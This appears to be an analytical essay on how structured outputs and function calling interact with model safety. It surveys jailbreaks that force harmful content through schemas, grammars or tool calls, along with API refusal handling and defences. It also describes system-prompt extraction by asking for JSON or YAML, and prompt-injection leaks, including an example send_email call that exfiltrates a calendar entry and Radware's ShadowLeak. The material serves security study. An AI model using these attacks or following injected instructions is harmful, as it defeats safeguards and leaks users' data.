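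It is harder to establish whether deployed classifiers check schemas and tool arguments. Anthropic's constitutional classifiers screen both a model's input and its output. The company trains them on examples generated from written rules about permitted and forbidden content. Claude Fable 5.1 also runs safety classifiers, according to Anthropic's *Migrating to Claude Fable 5.1 and Claude Mythos 5.1*, and a declined request returns a refusal marker and a category. Schemas reach the model as text, and tool arguments are part of what it generates, so classifiers that screen input and output could cover both.

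Anthropic warns that a schema property asking for the model's step-by-step reasoning may lead to a refusal, which is given its own category. The warning doesn't make clear whether a classifier checks the schema itself or the answer that the schema produces.

### What false alarms cost

Zhang and colleagues report detection rates for their guards but not the corresponding false-alarm rates, which may matter more for a busy service. If 100 of a million requests are attacks, a guard that catches 97.7% of attacks flags about 98 of them. If it also flags 1% of honest requests, it raises about 10,000 false alarms, so about 99% of the requests it flags are legitimate. To flag as many attacks as honest requests, it could wrongly flag only about one honest request in 10,000.

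The guard's errors would also be uneven across applications. An application sends much the same schemas all day, so a guard that wrongly blocks one of them will probably do so repeatedly. A moderation tool whose enum lists "self-harm" and "bomb threat" as categories might stop working altogether, while a weather service would be unaffected.

Heuristics that need less compute can also flag legitimate schemas. Zhang and colleagues suggest flagging schemas that contain a lot of fixed text relative to their structure, or that don't seem to fit the prompt. But a shop that lets a model choose from 500 product names has a schema made almost entirely of fixed text, and a general-purpose agent sends all its tools with every question, even though most are unrelated to it.

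Providers have accepted some of these drawbacks for their most capable models. AWS, Amazon's cloud service, says Claude Fable 5's classifiers block dual-use material in cybersecurity and biology, which could serve either defence or attack. It warns that refusal rates are "materially higher" than on earlier Claude models and tells customers to plan for refusals as a primary kind of response. It doesn't say what share of the refusals are mistakes.

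Anthropic runs a free verification programme for security professionals whose work resembles an attack. It covers the Opus and Sonnet models, and applicants must let the company retain their data. On Fable 5.1, a developer can also have a declined request fall back to another model. This keeps an agent running, but the fallback model may take over mid-task and call tools differently.

### Limits on size and nesting

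Providers also have a practical reason to check schemas, since compiling them takes work. According to *Get validated JSON results from models*, AWS's Bedrock service checks each schema against the part of the JSON Schema standard it supports and rejects the request if the schema uses anything else. Anthropic likewise rejects recursive schemas, which define a structure in terms of itself, such as a comment whose replies are also comments.

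Anthropic also allows at most 24 optional parameters and 16 parameters with alternative types across all the strict schemas in a request. Each optional parameter roughly doubles the number of possible states in part of the grammar, so ten affecting the same part would multiply that number by about a thousand. Anthropic sets further limits on the size of the compiled grammar and stops compilation after 180 seconds.

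A bug in the XGrammar engine shows what limits on schema size are for. *CVE-2025-58446* (2025), an entry in OSV, a public database of vulnerabilities in open-source software, describes an optimizer that was so slow on grammars of more than 100,000 characters that someone could stall a model provider with a huge enum. Version 0.1.24 fixed the bug, one version after the optimizer was introduced.

According to OSV's *CVE-2026-25048* (2026), the other bug let deeply nested syntax crash the program in versions before 0.1.32. The entry rates its severity at 8.7 out of 10. An attacker needed no privileges, but the flaw affected only the server's availability and exposed no data. Red Hat's *CVE-2026-25048* lists no workaround that meets the company's standards for ease of use and stability, so the remaining option is to upgrade. Anyone who runs such an engine should treat schemas from strangers like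 any other untrusted compiler input, and cap their size and depth before compiling them.

These limits constrain function calling. In Anthropic's example, four strict tools with six optional parameters each use up the whole allowance. The company suggests making parameters required, flattening nested objects, splitting the work across requests, or reserving strict mode for tools where a malformed call would cause real problems. The limits are inconvenient but predictable, because a schema that exceeds an explicit limit fails the first time the developer tries it. A guard model's mistakes may first appear in production, when a customer's wording triggers a false alarm.

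However, these limits do not stop jailbreaks. EnumAttack needs only a few short fields, so its schema passes all of these checks.

### Cached schemas and customers' own keys

Anthropic caches compiled grammars for 24 hours after their last use, so a schema that an application uses every day can stay cached indefinitely. A provider could reduce the computation needed for guarding in a similar way, by checking a schema once, when it compiles, and storing the verdict with the grammar. But Anthropic's API doesn't recompile a schema when only a name or description changes, and the model reads descriptions as text, so the verdict would need to be tied to the schema's full wording. Even then, the check would help only against requests whose harm is visible in the schema, because whether a request split between the schema and the prompt is harmful depends on the prompt too.

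Cached schemas also lack the privacy protections Anthropic gives to prompts and answers. Even under a zero-retention agreement, Anthropic stores schema information, including tool definitions, for up to 24 hours. It therefore tells healthcare customers to keep patient information out of property names, enums, fixed values and patterns.

This conflicts with the advice to use enums instead of free text. A clinic that limits a "patient" field to the names on today's list puts those names in the cache. It could use neutral codes in the schema and explain them in the prompt, but a joint guard might then flag the request as suspicious because its meaning is split between the two.

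Some customers who encrypt their stored data with a key they hold themselves can't use structured outputs with certain Anthropic models. An earlier version of Anthropic's *Customer-managed encryption keys* listed structured outputs as supported only on Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Claude Haiku 4.5. According to Anthropic's current retention page, a customer-managed key turns off structured outputs with Covered Models under Enterprise Frontier Safeguards, an arrangement that lets eligible organizations use those models without Anthropic storing their data.

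Anthropic doesn't give a reason for the restriction on that page, but the cache is a plausible one. The earlier version explains that the customer's key does not cover caches or data kept for less than 24 hours. Anthropic's current *Customer-managed encryption keys* says that within about an hour of a customer disabling the key, Anthropic can no longer decrypt the data the key protects. A compiled schema not covered by the key could remain available for most of a day after that. But this explanation doesn't account for the two models that did support the feature, and nothing connects the restriction to jailbreaks.

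These customers lose the guarantee that a tool call will match its schema. Fable 5.1 also rejects forced tool choice, so Anthropic tells them in its migration guide to name the tool in the prompt and rely on that instruction alone. Their own code then has to check every call and handle the malformed ones.

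## Refusing inside a forced call or a fixed format

Filters outside the model screen requests, but the model can also refuse a harmful request itself if the format allows a refusal. A forced function call may not allow one, an effect researchers first measured in 2024.

### The 2024 function-calling study

In *The Dark Side of Function Calling* (2024), Wu, Gao and colleagues made up a function, described it as a tool for writing fiction, and gave it one required argument to hold the harmful text. They forced the model to call the function, then read the argument. A 2023 attempt on GPT-4 by Kellin Pelrine and others had failed. Wu and colleagues think this was because Pelrine's team looked for harmful text in the model's final reply, when the weak point is the arguments the model writes earlier.

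With up to five attempts at each of 50 AdvBench requests, the attack succeeded 97% of the time on average across six models. The first attempt alone succeeded 85% of the time.

Wu and colleagues offer three explanations: safety training has covered function calls less than chat, a forced call gives the model no way to refuse, and providers' filters overlook arguments. They tested the first by pasting the function definition into an ordinary chat message, and the second by keeping the function but letting the model decide whether to call it.

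| Model | Forced call | Call the model could decline | Same text in chat |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 98% | 2% | 12% |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 98% | 34% | 0% |
| Gemini 1.5 Pro | 86% | 32% | 4% |

The paper takes the drop in attack success from the forced call (first column) to chat (last column) as confirmation that training on calls is weaker. But moving to chat also removes the forced call, so that comparison can't separate the effect of weaker training from the effect of forcing the call. Comparing the optional call with chat is better, because the model could refuse in both. On Claude and Gemini, the attack worked about a third of the time through an optional call and almost never in chat, which suggests a gap in training. On GPT-4o, it worked once in 50 tries through an optional call and six times in chat, so forcing the call explains nearly all of the 98% success rate in the first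 column.

There is less evidence for the third explanation. Gemini's safety filter blocked 34% and 30% of the requests in two comparison attacks that disguise them as code, but none in the function-calling attack. The filter may not have checked the arguments, or it may have checked them but failed to flag them because of the fictional framing.

Wu and colleagues discuss four defences, including these three. If the model could always decide whether to make a call, developers would have to write more precise prompts to get the calls they need. Safety training on calls requires new data and may make ordinary calls less accurate. Filters can miss encoded text that the model can still read.

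The fourth defense, the only one tested, is a sentence telling the model to check whether the function is safe and to return an apology as the argument if it isn't. Putting this sentence at the end of the function's description cut the attack's success rate to zero on the three models in the table and to 10% on an older GPT-4. When it was at the end of the user's message instead, the attack still succeeded 50% of the time on GPT-4o.

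The models could apparently recognize the harm once they had an instruction to look for it and somewhere to put a refusal. But the attacker writes the function's description, so the provider would have to add that instruction to every customer's tools. Wu and colleagues didn't measure how often models would then refuse when calling harmless functions, or say what a function would do with a refusal it received as an argument. A weather tool, for example, would presumably treat the refusal as a city name and try to look it up.

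### Refusals treated as errors

In *Beyond the Prompt*, Liu, Wang and colleagues (2026) reran the 2024 attack on newer models and compared it with their own, which uses what they call simulated moderation traces. Their attack presents the harmful request as part of a test of a content-moderation system and asks for the harmful text as a tool argument. If the model refuses, the attacker's program reports the refusal as a failed check and asks again. The attacker can invent both the tools and the errors because the application sends the model the conversation history with each request.

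The table shows success rates on the 50 requests in SafeBench-Tiny. A language model scored each answer from 0 to 5, and a score of 3 or more counted as a success. FCGuard is a defence that Liu and colleagues propose.

| Model | 2024 attack | Moderation traces | Same framing without function calls | Moderation traces with FCGuard |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 90% | 100% | 94% | 84% |
| GPT-5.4 | 48% | 100% | 76% | 0% |
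| Qwen3-Max | 88% | 100% | 100% | 86% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 84% | 100% | 50% | 20% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 98% | 100% | 100% | 92% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 26% | 98% | 0% | 0% |

Claude Sonnet 4.5 resists the 2024 attack much better than its predecessors did. On a second benchmark of 100 requests, that attack succeeded 5% of the time, while moderation traces succeeded 91% of the time and needed about two queries per request.

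The column without function calls is a cleaner version of Wu and colleagues' chat test. It keeps the framing, the examples and the invented errors but puts them in a plain conversation. The model can answer in prose in both versions. Removing the function calls cut the attack's success rate on Claude Sonnet 4.5 from 98% to zero. On Qwen3-Max, the rate was 100% either way, but when Liu and colleagues removed the repeated error messages, it fell to 98% with function calls and 50% without them. On DeepSeek-V4-Flash, function calls made almost no difference.

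Some models were still much easier to attack through function calls than through chat in 2026. This attack doesn't depend on forced tool choice, so it could work even on models that no longer accept that setting.

Liu and colleagues suggest a reason, based on Qwen3.5-9B, an open model whose prompt format they could inspect. The format puts tool definitions in the system message alongside the safety rules, so the attacker's text ends up in the part of the prompt with the highest priority. This would explain the results, but they didn't test whether moving the definitions elsewhere made the model safer.

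Conventional defences did little to stop the attack on Claude Sonnet 4.5. Screening the input with a separate model lowered the attack's success rate from 98% to 96%, and a safety reminder in the system prompt lowered it to 82%. Combining both with a length limit and less random sampling lowered it to 78%.

FCGuard is a longer system prompt that tells the model to look for malicious intent in the conversation, tool definitions, arguments and results. As the table shows, it worked completely on two models, fairly well on a third and poorly on the rest. The prompt also warns about specific disguises, including this attack's own, which is posing as a red-team test. Liu and colleagues didn't test an attack designed to avoid those warnings.

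FCGuard also made function calling less reliable. With it, GPT-5.4 refused 5.4% of 258 routine function-calling tasks, up from zero without it. If refusals were independent, an agent making 20 such calls per job would meet at least one refusal in about two out of three jobs. On 176 legitimate tasks that look sensitive, GPT-5.4's refusals rose from 10.2% to 22.7%. GPT-4o's rose from zero to 7.4%, even though the attack still succeeded against it 84% of the time.

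### When the grammar is harmless

CodeSpear, the attack by Zhang, Lu and Li, sends a malicious coding request with an off-the-shelf Python grammar. Unlike EnumAttack and DictAttack, it hides nothing in the schema, so a filter that inspects the grammar finds only the rules of Python.

The request itself is in the prompt in plain words, so an ordinary prompt filter could catch it. Zhang, Lu and Li exclude such filters from their threat model because anyone running a model privately can remove them and some providers won't accept the delay. Their results are therefore mainly about how well the model's own training resists the attack.

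The grammar raised the average success rate to 67.4% on commercial APIs, and from 54.9% to 81.8% on five open models run locally. When only code that did what was requested counted as a success, the rates rose from 11.0% to 36.6% on the API models and from 36.6% to 54.6% on the open ones. So only a little over half of the harmful answers from the API models did what was requested. A language model made these judgments by reading the code, and it agreed with human reviewers on 85–87% of a sample of 100 answers.

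GPT-5 resisted the attack better than most models. On RMCBench, a set of 182 malicious coding requests, its attack success rate rose from 32.1% to 55.5%. When the grammar prevented it from refusing in English, it often wrote `pass`, a Python statement that does nothing. After Zhang, Lu and Li removed `pass` from the grammar, the success rate rose to 70.3%.

An attacker who controls the grammar can also block any fixed form of refusal. For example, if a model always declined by writing "I'm sorry" in a JSON string, the attacker could write a schema that limits that string to values without the phrase.

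### Harmless code in place of a refusal

Ordinary safety training can make refusals more likely without making the remaining answers safer. Suppose a model answers a malicious coding request with a refusal 97% of the time, malicious code 2.7% of the time and unrelated harmless code 0.3% of the time. Restricting the output to Python with a grammar rules out the refusal, so malicious code makes up about 90% of what remains (2.7 of 3 percentage points). This figure is approximate because the grammar masks individual tokens rather than whole answers. More training might raise refusals to 99.7% and cut the other two shares to 0.27% and 0.03%, but under the grammar malicious code would still make up about 90% of answers.

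To be safe under the grammar, the model has to favor harmless code over malicious code. CodeShield, the defence that Zhang, Lu and Li propose, trains it to do so with direct preference optimization, which uses pairs of answers to the same prompt. Each answer *y* gets a score that depends on how much its probability has changed since training began:

s(y) = β × log(P_new(y) / P_old(y))

Here β is a constant that sets the scale. Training minimizes −log σ(s(better) − s(worse)), where σ maps any number to a value between 0 and 1. This loss falls as the better answer's score rises relative to the worse one's.

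CodeShield matches each of 2,000 malicious prompts with five random snippets of ordinary code. Each snippet produces two pairs, one that ranks a plain refusal above the snippet and one that ranks the snippet above malicious code, for 20,000 pairs in all. Training on these pairs should teach the model to refuse in English when it can and write harmless code when it can't. Zhang, Lu and Li call the harmless code honeypot code, and they vary it so that an attacker can't remove it by banning one statement.

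The table gives averages over two sets of malicious requests, with the Python grammar enforced. The last column is the share of ordinary programming problems the model solved on its first attempt, before and after CodeShield.

| Model | No extra training | Refusal training only | CodeShield | Ordinary problems solved |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-Coder-7B | 83.1% | 77.4% | 5.6% | 68.6% → 66.9% |
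| Qwen2.5-7B | 84.3% | 45.5% | 5.6% | 49.3% → 51.5% |
| Llama 3 8B | 66.7% | 46.6% | 7.9% | 53.7% → 46.9% |

Refusal training alone helped two of the three models somewhat, presumably because it also penalizes malicious code directly. CodeShield did far better on all three. Zhang, Lu and Li then had another model revise the grammar up to ten times per request to exclude whatever harmless code the target model returned, and the attack still succeeded less than 13% of the time. But this attacker changed only the grammar, whereas circuit breakers, another training-based defence, failed mainly against a combined prompt and schema attack. It's also unclear how well CodeShield would work on larger models.

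Llama 3 8B lost nearly seven percentage points on ordinary problems, a drop that Zhang, Lu and Li consider acceptable. Those problems are general exercises, so the scores don't measure how often a security engineer with a legitimate but suspicious-looking request would get a random snippet.

Such mistakes could be serious because nothing marks honeypot code as a refusal. CodeShield's refusals are therefore hard for legitimate software to detect, as well as hard for an attacker to remove. An attacker will see at once that the code is useless and try again, but an automated build might save or run it. The equivalent in a function call would be a well-formed argument for the wrong thing, such as a refund on someone else's order.

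### OpenAI's refusal field

OpenAI's API reports a refusal separately from the JSON that the schema describes, so the calling program has to check for one before it parses the answer. It must also check why generation ended, because an answer that hits the token limit or triggers OpenAI's content filter may contain only part of the JSON.

The Chat Completions API returns a refusal as a field of the message. The Responses API returns it as a separate type of item in the message's content, and when the answer streams, the refusal arrives as its own series of events. Client libraries also need to support the field. *Add refusal* (qhenkart, 2024) added it to a Go library in September 2024. Before then, programs that relied on the library's response type had no refusal field to check.

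Developers in the OpenAI forum thread *All "refusal" keys are null, even if refusal is true* complain that the `refusal` field stays empty when a model declines. One eventually got the field filled in by using a strict JSON schema. The API may fill it in only when a schema applies and otherwise leave the model to decline in ordinary text, which would explain this result. Code that handles requests both with and without a schema therefore shouldn't treat an empty field as proof that the model complied.

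OpenAI's guide describes the refusal field for formatted answers, not function calls, so developers who force a call should test what a refusal looks like in one. GPT-5 wrote `pass` statements when held to a code grammar, which suggests that it either had no separate way to refuse or didn't use one.

### Anthropic's refusal stop reason

In Anthropic's API, a refusal arrives as a successful response with HTTP status 200, and the customer pays for the tokens generated. A program that checks only for errors will miss the refusal, so the program must check the stop reason before using the content. The sample refusal in Anthropic's *Refusals and fallback* has an empty content list, which would crash code that assumes there is a first item.

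Anthropic's *Handle streaming refusals* distinguishes three cases. When a safety classifier stops an answer, the response has the stop reason `refusal`. A request that fails validation returns a 400 error. When the model itself declines, the refusal is ordinary text.

The last case is hard to reconcile with Anthropic's guide to structured outputs, which says that a refusal takes precedence over the schema and has the special stop reason. A classifier can stop the answer regardless of what the grammar allows, but the mask could block the model's own refusal if that refusal is ordinary text. Neither guide resolves this, so it would be safer for a program to also check the string fields of a valid object for an apology.

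A model that thinks before it answers may be more likely to notice a harmful request, because Anthropic doesn't apply the grammar to the thinking. On models that still allow forced tool calls, forcing a call removes that opportunity because the API skips the thinking.

Anthropic warns that after a classifier refusal, refusals will continue unless the application removes or rephrases the turn that caused the first one. In a tool-use loop, that turn may contain a web page the agent has just fetched, so anyone who can edit such a page may be able to halt the agent by adding text that triggers the classifier. A refusal can also interrupt a streamed tool call, and the application should then discard the incomplete arguments.

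In batch jobs, a refused request comes back marked "succeeded". In Anthropic's hosted agent service, a refused turn can end with the same stop reason as a normal one, so the program has to check a second field.

### A "cannot comply" value in the schema

Developers can also build a refusal into the schema. OpenAI suggests telling the model to return empty parameters or a set sentence when the input doesn't suit the task. This covers failures unrelated to safety. In the forum thread *Instruct refusal when using Model response format*, for example, a developer wanted the model to decline when an image contained nothing to extract.

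A dedicated alternative is easier to detect than an empty string. This schema for a weather request accepts either a location or a reason for declining:

```json
{
  "type": "object",
  "properties": {
    "result": {
      "anyOf": [
        {
          "type": "object",
          "properties": {"city": {"type": "string"}},
          "required": ["city"],
          "additionalProperties": false
        },
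        {
          "type": "object",
          "properties": {"cannot_comply": {"type": "string"}},
          "required": ["cannot_comply"],
          "additionalProperties": false
        }
      ]
    }
  },
  "required": ["result"],
  "additionalProperties": false
}
```

The schema needs the outer "result" field because OpenAI doesn't accept alternatives at the top level. The program always receives valid JSON, but it must check which alternative the model chose before it calls the weather service. Otherwise, it may treat a refusal as data.

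Anthropic allows at most 16 fields with alternatives, so an agent with the maximum of 20 strict tools can't offer this choice in all of them. A fixed word in an enum avoids that limit, though the program should ignore capitalization when it checks for the word.

This design helps an honest developer whose users or documents supply content the model shouldn't process, but it can't stop a malicious developer, who will leave the option out.

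### Refusal tokens that no grammar can mask

The provider could instead reserve a token that means "refuse" and keep it available under every schema, as the EnumAttack paper proposes. The OpenAI and Anthropic guides don't describe such a token. The closest mechanism they document is a separate classifier that stops the answer.

In the earlier example, "Sorry" had a logit of 6 and the opening brace had 2. If a reserved refusal token had the same logit as "Sorry" and the mask always allowed it, the model would refuse with probability 403.4 / (403.4 + 7.4), or about 98%, even though the schema required a brace. The model could also stop in the middle of a sentence that EnumAttack was forcing it to write, because the mask would allow two tokens at each step instead of one.

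The model would need training to use the refusal token partway through an answer as well as at the start. Otherwise, an attacker who forces the model to begin by agreeing could make the token as unlikely as any other late refusal. The provider would also have to keep customers from writing the token into a prompt or schema. Anyone running an open model privately could still remove the token from the engine.

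A refusal token that the model could choose at any step would create a new source of errors in harmless calls. If the model chose it by mistake once in every 100,000 tokens, a 500-token argument would fail about 0.5% of the time, and an agent that wrote 50 such arguments would have about a 22% chance of at least one false refusal. A provider could accept the token only above a minimum probability, which would prevent many of these mistakes but might also let some harmful answers through.

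The calling program would have to handle an object that breaks off at any point, much as it already must when an answer reaches the token limit. OpenAI recommends streaming for developers who want to handle function arguments as soon as they are available. A program that did this might already have started to send an email or change a file when a reserved refusal token arrived, so it would have to wait for the complete call before doing anything it couldn't undo.

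## A support assistant that leaked its internals as JSON

The attackers in the previous sections called a model's API directly, but some attackers can only use a company's chat box. *I'll Have a Raw JSON, Please* (El Yadini, 26 November 2026) describes an authorized attack of this kind by the security company Quarkslab on a client's customer-support assistant. The assistant refused every direct question about itself but disclosed much of its internal state when the testers asked for raw JSON.

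### 129 failures before the first leak

The testers made more than 200 attempts. The first 129 all asked the assistant to say something about itself, and all failed. Some attached such a question to a legitimate one, and others used role play, obfuscated wording, fake debugging output or fake tool results. Formatting tricks aimed at the system prompt also failed.

In attempt 130, the testers stopped asking for information about the assistant and only specified the format of its answer. That attempt also failed, but the next one worked. El Yadini illustrates the method with an ordinary question about an insurance claim, asked twice. The assistant first answers in prose, but when asked for raw JSON, it returns the unedited output of the tool that looked up the claim.

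In this way the testers obtained:

- the router that passes each question to an agent, and details of the agents themselves
- the tools and the arguments of the calls to them
- the output of the assistant's safety classifier
- internal procedures written for support staff, with the documents' metadata

Once the method worked, a short script was enough to collect the knowledge base one subject at a time, but the system prompt never leaked.

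Some of the leaked information would help with a second attack. For example, someone who can see the classifier's output can keep rewording a message until the classifier stops flagging it.

### The client's system and the reconstruction

To protect the client, El Yadini demonstrates the attack on a mock assistant for a fictional health insurer. It has a router, five agents, four tools, a safety classifier and four invented internal procedures. Like the client's assistant, it runs on LangChain, an open-source framework that connects models to tools and documents. It uses GPT-4.1 mini as a stand-in because the testers didn't know which model the client used.

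The count of failed attempts comes from the client's system, which was still in pre-production. The reconstruction is simpler and deliberately vulnerable, because its server returns whatever the model generates. So the reconstruction shows how the leak works, but not how often such an attack would succeed.

The client's application seems to have been built with similar carelessness. Its answers included LangChain run identifiers, which let the testers recognize the framework. Anyone who inspects the traffic can read such details, even if the web page doesn't display them.

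A model asked for its configuration may also make one up. The testers replayed promising messages in fresh sessions until they worked reliably, which rules out a fluke, but the model could still have made up the same answer each time. The people who built the reconstruction could at least compare its answers with the real configuration.

### Asking for JSON in plain words

The testers asked for JSON in the chat, so their request was entirely on the data plane and the attack didn't depend on constrained decoding. No mask prevented the model from refusing, even on attempt 131. The attack would still work if every provider withdrew structured outputs.

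The more likely cause is that the model treated the request as a formatting job. Sahu, Samanta and Soosahabi (2026) tested this in *Evaluation and Hardening of LLM System Instructions Against Extraction via Encoding Attacks*. They wrote 80 system prompts containing confidential details and kept the 46 that their models did not disclose when asked directly. They then asked for the same instructions in various formats. The table shows how often GPT-4.1 mini, the model in the reconstruction, disclosed something. YAML and TOML are notations for configuration files, and Base64 is a way of encoding data as plain characters.

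| Requested format | Original prompt | Rewritten prompt |
|---|---|---|
| YAML | 95.7% | 63.0% |
| TOML | 91.3% | 41.3% |
| JSON | 23.9% | 4.3% |
| Base64 | 8.7% | 0% |

These rates overstate how much an attacker would learn, because a fragment or a paraphrase counted as a leak. The effect is still large, since the direct questions had produced no leaks. It also doesn't seem to be limited to JSON. GPT-4.1 mini disclosed far more in YAML, perhaps because a system prompt resembles a configuration file.

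For the last column, a reasoning model had rewritten each prompt's loose confidentiality statement as explicit rules that override any other request. Leaks in YAML fell from 60.9% to 4.3% on Gemini 2.5 Flash, but only from 89.1% to 54.3% on Llama 3 8B. Sahu and colleagues did not measure whether the stricter prompts made assistants refuse ordinary formatting requests. A company that relies on wording alone would have to test its own model for both leaks and these refusals, and repeat the tests whenever the model changed.

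### Why the model had the data

An assistant has to look up a claim to tell a customer whether it has been paid. Function calling leaves both the call and its result in the conversation the model reads, so if the claims tool returns the complete record, the model receives the staff's notes along with the payment date.

Function calling requires some of this information. The model has to read the payment date to report it, and it has to see its earlier calls to keep track of what it has done. It doesn't need the staff's notes, and it probably doesn't need the safety classifier's output, which was presumably in the context because the application passed along more than it had to.

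### Filtering the answer

El Yadini concludes that only output filtering reliably prevents the leak, because a guardrail in the system prompt depends on how the question is worded, and an attacker can always reword it. The leaked data still has to appear in the answer, where a filter can catch it. Filtering the final answer also doesn't interfere with function calling, because the agent has finished using its tools by then.

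But the filter must be told what to look for. This is easiest with a single known secret, such as a password. *The Framing Gap* (2026) tests a guard that replaces the secret with a marker in outgoing messages and blocks calls that would send it to an untrusted service. The paper reports no leaks of the secret in plain text, but notes that this follows from the guard's definition. It calls the protection "surface-bound" because the guard detects the secret only in the form it was given.

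The support assistant's leak was harder to define. Suppose staff follow an internal procedure of waiving a fee for customers who complain twice. A filter could block the procedure's exact text, but the model's output could still reveal the rule in different words. A good answer to a customer may also use information from the same document, so the filter can't block all text that resembles the procedure.

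Standard filters cover only part of this. AWS lists personal data, credentials and types of information defined by the company using the filter. The name of an internal agent or the text of a procedure would fall into the last group, so the company would have to anticipate it. Filtering personal data can also block legitimate answers, such as telling customers which phone number the company has on file for them. LangChain's guidance describes rule-based checks as fast and cheap but liable to miss subtle violations, while checks by another model catch more and cost more.

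A company could block every support chat answer that is valid JSON with little disruption, because customers rarely need JSON and the application handles the JSON in tool calls separately. This would have stopped the leak in the form El Yadini shows, but the next customer could ask for YAML, a table or a bulleted list. The filter would have the same weakness as the guardrail it replaced, because it would recognize only one way of presenting the data.

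So a filter is worth having, particularly for credentials, but it isn't the only defence. Two others don't need to recognize a leak.

### Keeping data out of the context

A model can't disclose information it never received. OWASP, a nonprofit that publishes widely used lists of software risks, advises developers in *LLM07:2025 System Prompt Leakage* not to treat the system prompt as a secret or a security control, and to keep credentials out of it. The same reasoning applies to tool results, so the application shouldn't give a customer-facing model any result the company wouldn't want customers to read.

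The application can trim the result before adding it to the conversation. LangChain's *artifact* attribute holds the part of a tool's output that isn't meant for the model. A claims tool could put the status and payment date in the message and leave the staff's notes in the artifact. The knowledge base could also return only documents that the customer is allowed to read. A request for raw JSON would then produce an odd-looking but harmless answer.

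This takes work for every tool, and some tasks need data that the model shouldn't see. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes an agent, FIDES, that can store a sensitive result in a variable and show the model only the variable's name. The model can still put a variable such as `read_emails_0` in a message to a colleague, and the software fills in the contents when it makes the call. With security checks switched off, the extra machinery reduced the agent's usefulness by 6.3% on AgentDojo, a benchmark of agent tasks.

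In its standard form, FIDES wouldn't have stopped this leak. It assumes that the user is trustworthy and the danger comes from outside data, so it checks tool calls but not answers to the user. Costa and colleagues note that the same checks can run on answers, which a public support assistant would need.

Variables don't help when the model has to understand the data. A model can use a variable to forward an email without reading it, but it has to read the refund rules to decide whether a customer qualifies. If those rules are confidential, the company has to either write a version that customers may see or control what the model can say after reading them.

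### A response schema with no field for internal data

Structured output offers a way to exercise that control. The developer requires every answer about a claim to match a schema like this one:

```json
{
  "type": "object",
  "properties": {
    "claim_status": {
      "enum": ["received", "in_review", "paid", "declined"]
    },
    "next_step": {
      "enum": ["none", "wait", "send_documents", "contact_support"]
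    }
  },
  "required": ["claim_status", "next_step"],
  "additionalProperties": false
}
```

The application then uses the two values to pick a sentence from a fixed list. If a customer asks for raw JSON, the model might otherwise output the claim record, but the mask blocks every token that could begin it. EnumAttack uses the same mechanism to block refusals, but here an honest developer controls it. The application must also replace any answer that doesn't fit the schema, such as one cut short by a length limit, with a standard message.

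The schema allows 4 × 4 = 16 different answers, so each answer carries at most log₂ 16 = 4 bits. A 1,000-byte document contains up to 8,000 bits. Even if an attacker persuaded the model to encode the document in the two fields, copying it without compression would take 2,000 answers. Costa and colleagues rank output types by the same measure. A true-or-false value carries less than an enum, which carries less than a string, since a string has no fixed limit.

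However, the schema could still leak very small secrets. Whether the insurer suspects a customer of fraud is a single bit, and an attacker might get the model to reveal it by choosing "wait" for yes and "none" for no. So although the schema would protect the internal procedures well, it would do little to protect the classifier's flags. Those flags are better kept out of the context, which should be easy because the model doesn't need them to answer.

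One free-text field can undo most of the benefit. Praetorian's *Exploiting LLM Write Primitives* describes an administrative assistant that replied in chat only with fixed templates but could fill in forms. The security company's testers got it to write encoded pieces of its system prompt into an email field, about 100 characters at a time, until they had the whole prompt. Praetorian recommends checking that an email field contains a valid address. This would make the attack harder, but a valid address can still hold quite a few arbitrary characters.

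OpenAI's *Safety in building agents* also treats fixed formats as a defence. It advises developers to pass data between an agent's steps in enums and fixed schemas, and says that structured outputs and isolation "greatly reduce, but don't fully remove" the risk from text that influences tool calls.

A response schema can also interfere with function calling. *Constraint Tax in Open-Weight LLMs* (2026) examines how such constraints can suppress tool calls in models with published weights, so that the model fills in the answer without looking anything up. The support assistant could then return a correctly formatted claim status that it never looked up.

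A developer can avoid this by applying the schema only after the tools have run. *SPA* (2026), a design for agents that keep working across several requests, gives some steps to an isolated model that has no tools and must answer in a set schema. The support assistant could similarly use one model to call the tools without a response schema and a second to read the results and fill in the two enums. If the company wanted friendlier prose than fixed sentences allow, a third model could write the reply from those two values, the customer's question and the public help pages. If a customer asked the third model for JSON, YAML or any other format, it couldn't reveal the internal record because it would never have received it. The company would pay for two more model calls per answer, and a person would have to handle questions that the enums didn't cover.

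## Secrets leaving an agent through tool arguments

The support assistant leaked its data to the person chatting with it. An agent with tools can also leak data to someone who can't see the conversation, because each argument it writes goes to whoever runs the tool or receives what the tool sends.

### A leak inside a valid call

Suppose a user asks an agent to accept a picnic invitation if the date is free. The agent can read email, read the calendar and send email.

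1. The agent reads the invitation. It contains a sentence in white type, invisible to the user, which asks for the title of the guest's next appointment to be included in the reply.
2. The agent reads the calendar, which it has to do anyway to find out whether the date is free. The appointment is now in its context.
3. The agent follows the hidden sentence as if the user had written it, and calls the email tool.
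4. The application checks the call against the tool's schema, finds nothing wrong and sends the email.

The call looks like this:

```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "arguments": {
    "to": "picnic@example.org",
    "body": "Yes, I'll be there. Dentist, Tuesday 3 p.m."
  }
}
```

The user had given the agent all three tools, the recipient is correct, and both arguments are strings, as the schema requires, so the call would also satisfy strict tool use. A JSON Schema can limit a value's type, length or pattern, but it has no keyword for where the value came from. The same email would have been appropriate if the user had asked the agent to mention the dentist.

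Reviewing the tool in advance doesn't help much either. *PACE* (Li, Wang et al., 2026) considers a mail tool whose code sends whatever body the model writes. In one version, the tool's description tells the model to use a fixed template. In another, it tells the model to copy a credential from the conversation. The code and interface are identical, so a reviewer who relies on those can't tell the versions apart. The paper argues that the last useful place for a check is immediately before the call runs, when the software has the actual arguments, the user's request and a record of what the agent has read.

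### ShadowLeak

*ShadowLeak*, by the security company Radware, documents a leak of this kind in Deep Research, the ChatGPT mode that spends up to half an hour gathering material for a report. A user could connect it to Gmail and let it browse the web at the same time. Radware's researchers wrote an email with hidden instructions. When the user later asked Deep Research to go through the day's messages, the agent took an employee's name and address from a different email and opened a URL that contained them. This happened without the user clicking anything or seeing any sign of it.

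The agent sent the data out in the URL argument it gave the browsing tool. Requesting a page sends its full URL to the site, and sites commonly log those URLs, so the site's owner gets any text in the URL even if the page is blank. The demonstration took one employee's details, but the agent could read the connected inbox. Radware demonstrated the attack only with Gmail but expects the same pattern to work with other sources that users could connect, such as Google Drive and GitHub.

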